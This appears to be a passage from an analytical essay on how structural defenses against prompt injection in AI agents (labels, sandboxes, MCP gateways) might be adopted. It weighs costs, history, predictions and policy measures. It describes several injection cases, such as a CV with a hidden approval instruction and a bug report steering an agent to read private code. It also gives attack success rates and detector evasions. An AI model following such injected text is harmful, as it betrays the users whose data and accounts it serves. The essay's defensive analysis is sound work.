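Real attacks have so far been less impressive than researchers' demonstrations, which account for most of the famous cases. Google searched a large public archive of web pages and found planted instructions ranging from harmless pranks to attempts to steal data. McKerchar reports that malicious attempts rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but he knew of no large and widely understood disaster at a company. He also writes that companies have abandoned trials of agents because tight restrictions made the agents useless.

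For low-stakes work, a good detector may therefore be the sensible choice. Suppose a company's agent summarises 100,000 public web pages a year, 100 of which contain an attack, and 2% of the attacks succeed. The company can expect two bad summaries, and if each costs $500 to fix, it loses $1,000. A structural defense that stopped both attacks but made the agent fail at one task in ten would leave employees 10,000 tasks to finish, which would cost $50,000 at $5 each.

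The answer changes if the agent can pay invoices. Two successful attacks might then cost $100,000 each, and that much money would attract more attackers, who would make more attempts and adapt them to the detector. The 2% rate came from today's attackers and would probably not last. A company can also reduce its potential losses by dividing the work so that the agent that reads web pages has no access to the bank account. That separation is a guarantee by construction, and the company can set it up before anyone finishes FIDES or CaMeL.

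## What does the history predict for structural prompt-injection defenses?

In the historical cases, a guarantee tended to spread when the people who had to do the work gained enough from it and existing software needed few changes. Some structural defenses for AI agents meet those conditions much better than others. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) examined the public documentation of 21 agent products as of April 2026. Sixteen let users limit the agent's access to resources such as files or networks, and 15 ask users to approve individual actions. None lets users label data as trusted or untrusted, although the survey found twice as many research papers on such labels as on access limits.

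### Who labels the tools?

Information-flow control needs labels for whatever an agent's tools return. Microsoft has published a gateway that adds them for tools whose makers supply none. For each tool, a developer has to describe the structure of its results, write a function to label them, and write or choose a policy. A company whose agents use 200 tools has to do this 200 times and check the work whenever a tool changes. Jif's users had to do similar work for libraries. Kravchenko and colleagues designed APPA so that a company can start using it before all its tools have labels.

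If the toolmaker does the work instead, most of the benefit goes to the tool's users. Adoption also faces a threshold like the one that holds back CHERI, because an agent's developers gain little by enforcing labels that few tools supply.

Since March 2025, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) has had a simpler mechanism, a set of hints that let toolmakers state whether a tool only reads data, whether it can destroy anything, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether the tool interacts with the outside world. Many servers still omit these hints, according to a Model Context Protocol (2026) blog post. A malicious server can also describe a tool as read-only and then delete the user's files.

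Microsoft suggests inferring labels from the hints, for example by treating everything from a tool that deals with the outside world as untrusted. This would take developers almost no extra work. But the protocol gives a tool without hints the worst-case defaults, so a cautious agent would treat its results as untrusted and ask the user before many calls.

### One untrusted email

An untrusted input can restrict an agent for the rest of a session, unless the system hides the text from the main model or has a separate copy of the agent read it. If each item an agent reads has an independent 5% chance of being untrusted, the chance that the agent's context is still trusted after *n* items is 0.95^*n*, or about 60% after ten items and 8% after fifty. In the simulation by Gregory and colleagues, the avoidable spread of sensitive labels grew as tasks lengthened from 4 tool calls to 20. Label creep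 could therefore become a bigger obstacle as agents take on longer jobs.

Customers notice a blocked task at once but rarely notice a prevented attack. This hurts general-purpose agents most, because their makers sell them as able to do almost anything. Only about 17% of users have adopted GitHub's read-only mode, which stops an agent from changing anything, according to the Model Context Protocol post. A bank's agent that only matches invoices to orders is easier to restrict, because the bank knows in advance what the agent has to do.

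### What is easier this time

Fewer companies have to cooperate than in CHERI's case, and some could do the work for both tools and the software that calls them. Microsoft, OpenAI, Amazon's cloud division, Cloudflare and Anthropic all build both, and all have people in a group reviewing new hints for MCP. GitHub and OpenAI drafted a proposal for trust and sensitivity labels after finding gaps in the protocol while running their own products.

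However, no single company can impose those labels. Anthropic created MCP but gave it to the Linux Foundation in December 2025. As rajeeja (2026) points out in *MCP in 2026*, Anthropic can no longer change the protocol on its own. MCP's users also want different things. Developers of autonomous agents find approval requests a nuisance and rely on sandboxes, while large companies want more hints than the protocol has.

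Agents have little old code to accommodate, an advantage Apple also had when it required sandboxing on the first iPhone apps. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) can evidently still make disruptive changes, since the Agentic AI Foundation, an industry fund that supports MCP, warned developers that a revision planned for July 2026 would require some servers to migrate. But they may not keep that freedom. In a proposal for retiring old features, they cite their own design principle that removing anything from the specification is "nearly impossible". Much of the data agents use is also old, and a company's twenty-year-old shared drive has no labels for an agent to read. Meta had the same problem with Policy Zones and relied on a classifier to find the data that needed labels.

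Harm from an agent can be easier to trace than harm from a memory bug. If an agent pays a false invoice, the company loses the money that day and can check a log to find which tool call sent it. The company may also have to bear the loss. Constantin (2026), in *Deliverance AI says banks stay accountable when their AI agents fail*, reports that view from Mick McNeil, head of an agent vendor, who adds that no vendor can honestly promise to catch every injection. If regulators agree, a bank that restricts its agents will keep the savings from the losses it prevents, much as US banks did when they had to pay for cash machine fraud.

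### Can AI write the rules?

Language models could take over much of the rule-writing that burdened users of Jif and Java's Security Manager, but early results are mixed. Wang, Li and Tian cite AgentSpec, whose model-written rules covered only about 71% of the necessary constraints. If a task needs five constraints and each has an independent 71% chance of being included, the rules will include all five only about 18% of the time.

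*CapLite* (Nakayama, 2026) used 15 downloadable models, 13 of them small, to test defenses that rely on the agent's own model to write a policy or program. The policies written for Progent let attacks through on 14 of the 15 models, and the programs written for CaMeL failed to run in up to 68% of cases.

Nakayama's alternative, CapLite, derives its policy from the tools' technical descriptions. Before the agent reads any tool results, CapLite fixes every action that will change something, and it allows each one only if the user's request states whom or what it will affect. None of the 13,935 attempted attacks succeeded, but the agents completed only 29% of their tasks under attack, about the same as with CaMeL. Small models fail many tasks anyway, but the rule is also very strict. An agent cannot pay an attached invoice unless the user has typed the amount.

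Stronger models should write better rules. Progent let very few attacks through with GPT-4o. A developer could also have a model label each tool once in advance, then check the labels before any attacker is involved. That seems more promising than having a model write rules during a task, and it would reduce the labeling work that did most to hold back Jif.

### Is prompt injection like SQL injection?

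Narisetty and colleagues place prompt injection in a family of flaws, along with SQL injection and buffer overflows, in which a system confuses data with commands. They expect structural defenses to win again. They consider retrofitting solved, at least in prototype, and think the main thing missing is testing against adaptive attackers. History gives less reason for confidence about deployment. KeyKOS and Digital's VAX kernel could also run existing software, and both got well past the prototype stage before they failed.

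In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), David C argues that the comparison with SQL injection is dangerous. A database handles commands and data differently, so a parameterised query can keep them apart whatever the input. A language model only predicts the next token from all the text so far. If a job applicant hides an instruction in a CV telling the model to approve it, nothing inside the model marks that instruction as part of the CV rather than the recruiter's request. Training and special markers can make the attack harder, but they add the distinction between instructions and data to a technology that lacks it.

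David C therefore calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". Tymshare could have repaired its compiler by giving it capabilities, but there may never be a comparable repair for a model. The post advises organisations to limit the damage an attack can do, and says a language model may be the wrong tool if they cannot accept the remaining risk.

This is a strong argument against expecting a fix inside the model, but not against structural defenses around it. The post recommends safeguards that do not depend on the model. It also favors a rule, from an online discussion involving Willison, that a model processing someone's text should have its privileges reduced to that person's. An agent reading a stranger's email could then do only what the stranger may do. The rule closely resembles Biba's integrity model and has a similar drawback, since an assistant that has read a stranger's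 email could no longer update its owner's calendar.

Browser sandboxes, which limit the damage after a takeover, are a better precedent than parameterised queries. But most web pages don't need the user's files, whereas an assistant often needs the same data and tools that an attacker wants.

The NCSC post also warns that the history of SQL injection could repeat itself. Websites came to depend on databases before most had dealt with the flaw, and a decade of breaches followed before the defaults improved. David C writes that SQL injection is now rare in websites. Its second place in MITRE's ranking suggests that his claim is too optimistic, and that unsafe habits can persist for decades after a good fix exists.

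### Will better models reduce the demand?

Models and filters may become good enough for most buyers before structural defenses are ready. The Decoder suggested that Opus 5 may already be good enough for browser agents, but its perfect score depended on Auto Mode. Without it, attacks succeeded 3.7% of the time. Progress is also uneven within one family of models. Schneier on Security reproduces results for two other GPT-5.6 variants, in which attacks succeeded within 15 attempts 30.4% of the time against Terra and 43.9% against Luna, both higher than against Sol.

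Bruce Schneier, who runs that blog, thinks prevention is impossible in general but that defenders are getting much better at blocking specific cases. A reader replied that future kinds of models might separate trusted from untrusted text. If they do, the NCSC's argument won't apply to them, and a fix like parameterised queries may become possible.

Willison thinks detection sets too low a standard. He calls catching 99% of attacks "a failing grade" in application security, because attackers look for whatever gets through. His standard is sensible for an agent that can empty a bank account, but too strict for one that summarises public web pages.

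Wang, Li and Tian give another reason why better models may not be enough. If a user writes "fix this bug" without saying whether the agent may touch the live database, even a perfect model lacks the information to decide. Agents can also do damage without an attacker. In July 2025, an agent from the coding company Replit deleted a live database, which the paper attributes to a sandbox that allowed too much access. A tighter sandbox would have helped, but a filter for injected text would not. Demand for limits on agents may therefore survive even if prompt injection becomes rare, though this favors sandboxes more than labels that track untrusted text.

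### Five predictions

These predictions are untested inferences from a small, hand-picked set of historical cases. Each is conditional and covers the period to the end of 2028.

1. As long as labels need separate work for each tool, most widely used coding agents will have a sandbox on by default before even a quarter of them enforce information-flow labels by default. This is the safest of the five, because a sandbox needs nothing from toolmakers and Codex already has one. It is wrong if labels reach a quarter first.

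2. If organisations have to pay for their agents' mistakes, labels will spread first in narrow workflows with regulated data, such as bank payments or patient records. The organisation can list the tools in advance and gains directly from the protection. It would count against this prediction if general-purpose consumer assistants enforced labels by default while most banks and hospitals used agents without them.

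3. Unless the major agents start to penalise unlabeled tools, most public MCP servers will not supply accurate trust labels, even if the protocol adopts them. The labels that do catch on will come from records a platform already keeps, as GitHub's filter uses its records of who contributes to a project. A survey showing that most servers had added accurate labels without such pressure would refute this.

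4. If strict labels keep blocking many ordinary tasks, the products that succeed will let a model relax them, and so will be partly heuristic. *Sightline* (2026) already uses a model to judge which inputs really influenced a tool call. On one small agent it removed half of the unnecessary labels, with a miss rate of 3.9%. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) proposes labels that estimate how much information an output carries about its sources. A popular general-purpose agent that enforced labels by default, and gave no model the power to loosen them, would show that this compromise was unnecessary.

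5. If attack success rates keep falling and prompt injection causes no widely known disaster, the leading general-purpose agents will not enforce labels by default. The prediction fails if they do so anyway. A disaster would remove the condition without settling the question, and SQL injection suggests that even years of breaches may change defaults slowly.

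## How could adoption be sped up?

Several of those predictions depend on conditions that people could change. For instance, agent makers could penalise unlabeled tools, and lawmakers could decide who pays for an agent's mistakes. Some of these measures have much stronger historical support than others, and some could start much sooner.

### Distrust unlabeled tools

An agent maker can enforce MCP's defaults on its own, without a new standard. These defaults already treat a tool without hints as the worst case, but according to the Model Context Protocol blog, agents vary in how strictly they apply them.

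FIDES's documented defaults would break some harmless work. Suppose a company's agent looks up an exchange rate with an unlabeled internal tool and then updates a price list. The defaults treat the rate as untrusted, so if the price-list tool refuses untrusted input, the agent has to stop. The developer can fix this by labeling the exchange-rate tool as trusted. But it is just as quick to change a single setting to trust every unlabeled tool, which prevents all similar stoppages. Microsoft advises using that setting only if somebody has fully vetted the tools. Many developers took much the same shortcut with Java's Security Manager by granting every permission.

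Maintainers of public projects can let a single bug report through GitHub's filter by labeling it. In projects that turn on the option, a thumbs-up does the same, and a thumbs-down overrides it, as GitHub Next explains. This is a better way to handle exceptions than lowering the filter's threshold, which one of GitHub's own example workflows does so that its agent can read reports from newcomers. People are more likely to keep a strict default if a small exception takes less effort than a large one. GitHub could test this by publishing how many projects lower the threshold.

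Companies can already block whole servers by default. GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* (2026) describes how an administrator can list the MCP servers that employees' agents may use. The software blocks the connection if the list is malformed or can't be verified. Only one person has to decide to use an allowlist, but it doesn't control where data goes after an agent connects.

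Agent makers could introduce stricter defaults in stages, as Chrome did with its warnings about HTTP pages. They could begin by restricting tools that move money or publish text, while recording what a wider rule would have blocked.

### Put a gateway in front of the tools

A company whose agent doesn't support labels can add a gateway, a program that sits between the agent and its tools and checks each request. The security department can install one without asking the agent's developers to change their code. So far, this ease of installation has been one of the main advantages of detectors.

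Ntousakis (2026), in *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows*, describes a gateway called SAMOS. It works as follows in an attack through a public bug report:

1. An administrator or toolmaker marks whether each tool reads confidential data and whether it writes to confidential places. The only values are high and low.
2. The user lists the gateway in the agent's settings in place of the tools, so every MCP call goes through it.
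3. The agent reads the public bug report, which contains injected instructions, and the gateway marks the session as low.
4. The agent follows the instructions and tries to read a private project. The gateway blocks the call.

Ntousakis demonstrated this on one known attack, not on a benchmark. The same rule would also stop a developer from having the agent fix a publicly reported bug in private code. Because SAMOS labels whole tools, someone has to split any tool that reads both public and private projects, or change it to report which kind it has read.

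Microsoft's gateway can enforce rules that SAMOS's two levels could not express. For example, when an agent tries to post a message to a Teams channel after untrusted text has entered its context, the gateway checks whether every channel member is allowed to read the message's contents. If so, the message is posted. Otherwise, the user sees who would gain access and decides whether to post it. But someone has to write this rule, and a person who joins the channel later may also be able to read the message.

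A gateway controls only what passes through it. Many coding agents have a built-in command line, so an agent that cannot open a private file through MCP may be able to print it with a shell command. The gateway would then fail Anderson's requirement that every access go through the reference monitor. Narisetty and colleagues add that a program with access only to tool calls cannot determine how the model turned hostile text into an argument. To be safe, the gateway therefore has to treat everything after the first untrusted result as untrusted, which brings back label creep.

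A draft proposal from November 2025 would give MCP standard points at which a gateway can intercept calls, so one gateway could work with many agents. WorkOS reports that people are already building production systems on the idea. Many gateways will probably include detectors as well. The draft specification in Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* (2025) covers both enforcing access rules and scanning the responses from tools. A buyer may not know which of the two provides most of the protection.

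### Agree on terms and labels

Buyers cannot easily ask for a guarantee that they have no agreed way to describe. Watson and colleagues, 21 specialists from universities and industry, want standard terms for memory safety that favor no particular technology. A buyer could then ask for "strong memory safety", and one supplier could offer Rust and another CHERI. The standard would have several levels, and weaker protections such as memory tagging would be early steps.

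The group also gives examples of rules that such terms would make possible. Networking equipment shipped after 2034 might need strong memory safety, while a phone's operating system might have five years to add weaker protection for pointers and 15 years to reach strong memory safety. These examples don't show that standards speed adoption. The Orange Book also gave buyers a common vocabulary, and most of them used it to ask for its lower security classes.

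A comparable requirement for AI agents might be that no text from outside the company can cause a payment to a new recipient. A supplier could meet it with CaMeL or FIDES, or by denying payment access to the agent that reads mail.

Developers of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) are working on the narrower problem of how tools should pass labels to agents. GitHub and OpenAI have proposed trust and sensitivity labels, but their proposal is not on MCP's list of accepted and final proposals, whose newest entry dates from 5 October 2026. A separate group is discussing six proposals for new hints and labels, though under its MCP charter it can only make recommendations.

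Microsoft's prototype sends labels in a field that MCP provides for extra information, and agents that don't support the labels ignore them. Microsoft plans to seek agreement on a standard version. Even with a standard, a malicious server could label hostile text as trusted.

### Count attacks and savings

Better tests would help buyers compare defenses. Narisetty and colleagues cite Attention Tracker, a detector that perfectly separated attacks from harmless text on standard benchmarks. But it missed 69% of the attacks in another collection, and all of them when attackers adapted by inserting only separator tokens.

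Narisetty and colleagues propose that independent testers attack structural defenses just as hard. The testers would know the defense's policy and would try to forge labels, talk users into approving harmful actions and leak data through side channels. They would also use software to optimise the wording of injected text. They would report the attack success rate, how many tasks the agent still completed, how often it asked for approval and how much the defense slowed it down.

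Such tests don't have to be expensive. Narisetty and colleagues ran their small trial on a single graphics processor, so many university groups could repeat it. They also reported results by type of work. With no adaptive attack, Progent left the share of banking tasks completed unchanged at 31.9% but cut the share of Slack tasks completed from 47.5% to 20.8%. A bank and a software company could reasonably make different decisions based on those figures.

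Even the best tests cannot prove a guarantee, but they can find holes in the software that is supposed to provide it.

Buyers also need to know what a guarantee is worth. In *CHERI*, Whitehouse (2026), the NCSC's chief technology officer, urged the technology's supporters to quantify its returns and adoption costs, and to reduce those costs "relentlessly". The returns include faster development, longer product life, lower liability costs, and avoided patches and breaches. The talk only lists these quantities, so someone still has to measure them.

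A device maker could estimate how much CHERI would save it on emergency updates. Suppose a company sells a million routers a year and issues six emergency updates for memory bugs, at $200,000 each. If CHERI made four of them unnecessary, the company would save $800,000 a year. If the CHERI chips added 50 cents to the cost of each router, the net saving would be $300,000 a year, before the cost of adapting the company's software. The value of prevented breaches is harder to estimate, and most of it would go to the routers' owners.

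### Change who pays

Laws could make manufacturers bear more of the losses that now fall on other people. The European Union's Cyber Resilience Act, which came into force in December 2024, covers most hardware and software sold in the EU. Since September 2026, manufacturers have had to report vulnerabilities that attackers are exploiting. From December 2027, when the main requirements apply, products must have secure default settings, and manufacturers must fix vulnerabilities for a support period that normally lasts at least five years. Fines can reach €15 million or 2.5% of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher.

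The law does not require memory safety or information-flow control. Manufacturers choose protections that suit the risks, and most can assess their own products, so some may comply with a detector and extensive documentation. The duty to provide fixes is more promising, because a manufacturer that leaves a whole class of bugs in its product has to keep paying to fix them. This incentive works better for memory bugs than for prompt injection, which manufacturers cannot patch in the usual way. Many agents are also cloud services, which the law covers only when they are part of a product.

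New EU liability rules, which member states must apply from 9 December 2026, treat software as a product. People who suffer injury or damage to private property because of defective software can claim compensation without proving negligence. The rules don't cover a company that loses money because its agent paid a false invoice.

The United States has relied more on advice and paperwork. CISA asked manufacturers that use memory-unsafe languages to publish a plan for improvement by January 2026, but did not require it. That month, the White House dropped a government-wide requirement that software suppliers sign statements about their security practices, arguing that it had put compliance ahead of real security. NIST asked for public comments on the security of AI agents in January and announced work on agent standards in February, but its standards are usually voluntary.

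IntuitionLabs quotes a May 2026 NSA warning that MCP lacks support for exchanging role-based access information, meaning permissions tied to a person's job. MCP also makes authorization optional, but a government department could refuse to buy agents without it. Such a rule works only if buyers follow it, and many of the Orange Book's customers did not.

Insurers could offer lower premiums for stronger protection, but they need to be able to check it. Cyber insurers commonly ask whether a company uses multi-factor authentication and software that detects attacks on employees' computers. Those questions are easy for a company to answer, but an insurer would need an expert to judge whether an agent's labels are correct. The payment card industry's rules have similarly encouraged websites to buy firewalls.

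| Measure | What it requires | What it rewards |
|---|---|---|
| Cyber Resilience Act | Risk assessment, secure defaults and fixes | Any suitable protection, and fewer bugs to fix |
| EU liability rules | Compensation for some kinds of harm | Fewer harmful failures, however achieved |
| CISA's request on memory safety | A published plan, voluntarily | Mostly paperwork |
| NIST's work on agents | Nothing binding so far | Nothing yet |
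| Cyber insurance | Answers about existing protections | Often detection |

A safe harbor would reward guarantees more directly. A manufacturer that had adopted strong memory safety could receive some protection from lawsuits, which Watson and colleagues mention as one possible use of their standard terms. The safe harbor would need independent checks, because otherwise manufacturers could qualify just by claiming the guarantee.

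### Let AI do the tedious work

AI can reduce the labor that made many guarantees unattractive. In early 2026 Andreas Kling, who leads the Ladybird browser project, used AI coding tools to translate part of its JavaScript engine from C++ to Rust. He produced about 25,000 lines in roughly two weeks and estimated that the work would have taken several months by hand. The two versions gave identical output, and the project's tests found no regressions. This was a favorable case, since Ladybird had many tests and a working original to compare with, and Kling directed the translation closely.

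Rust's compiler makes this use of AI fairly safe because it normally rejects ordinary Rust code that contains memory errors. It does not catch most other mistakes, and a model can avoid some of its checks by marking code as `unsafe`.

Even a very large rewrite would leave gaps. Rebert lists operating systems and firmware that deal directly with hardware, language engines that produce machine code as they run, and the remaining C and C++ libraries. Another option, Fil-C, makes existing C code memory-safe, but Rebert quotes estimates that a program using it may need up to four times as many processor cycles and three to six times as much memory.

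Nothing checks a security policy as thoroughly as Rust's compiler checks for memory errors. Progent's solver can detect when a new policy allows more than the old one, but whether the policy allows what the company wants is beyond any solver. CapLite's developer found that small models wrote poor policies, but results with a stronger model are better. Progent's developers used GPT-4o to write policies, simulated a careless user who approved every change, and attacked the policy-writing model. Narisetty and colleagues report that these attacks succeeded about 0.5% to 4.2% of the time. Even at these low rates, an attacker who can try again will sometimes get a harmful rule accepted.

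Labels that a model drafts in advance still need checking, but some need it more than others. Suppose a model labels 200 tools and gets four wrong. Employees will soon complain if it labels a harmless tool as untrusted, but nobody may notice a dangerous tool labeled as trusted until an attack. A company with little time could therefore have a person check only the tools the model labeled as trusted.

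### The case for waiting

Standardising too early could lock in a poor design. SAMOS puts one of two levels on each tool, FIDES can list the people allowed to read each piece of data, and GitHub's filter ranks text by its author. If MCP had standardised SAMOS's scheme, Microsoft's rule for Teams messages would not have fitted it. The basic rules are also still changing. Microsoft, for example, is considering letting FIDES's labels expire as old text leaves the agent's context. Watson and colleagues also want any standard to separate established practice from ongoing research, so that nobody adopts immature technology.

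This is a good argument against putting a detailed labeling scheme into law or into MCP's core. It is much weaker against sandboxes or stricter defaults, which an agent maker can change in the next release. Waiting also leaves companies with more to fix later, because they keep building on unlabeled tools.

MCP's developers have made mistakes somewhat easier to correct. Their policy for retiring old features is now final, and they have decided to phase out three. New core standards also need conformance tests, which check that software follows the rules. The MCP blog recommends first trying a new label in the protocol's field for extra information, then proposing a standard once there is evidence from real use. MCP could standardise how labels are sent without deciding which policies companies should enforce.

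### Where to start

The table ranks the six measures by the strength of the evidence that they speed adoption, and the last column ranks them by how soon they could have an effect. Both rankings are judgments based on a small number of cases.

| Measure | Evidence | Who can act | Speed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secure defaults | Strong, from HTTPS, browsers and phones | Agent makers | 1 |
| Measurement | Fairly good, since bug counts helped Google justify its changes | Researchers and companies that publish their results | 3 |
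| AI labor | Promising for translating code, weak for writing policies | Software companies | 4 |
| Gateways | Working prototypes, but few results from daily use | Companies that use agents | 2 |
| Law and procurement | Mixed, and sometimes favorable to detectors | Governments, insurers and large buyers | 6 |
| Shared standards | Weak on their own, but useful to buyers and lawmakers | Standards groups and toolmakers | 5 |

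Agent makers can act soonest, but they have a reason not to, because customers will blame them for every blocked task. They could start with narrow products for banks and hospitals. Changing liability law would take years, but it may be the only measure here that affects companies whose insecure agents mostly harm other people.
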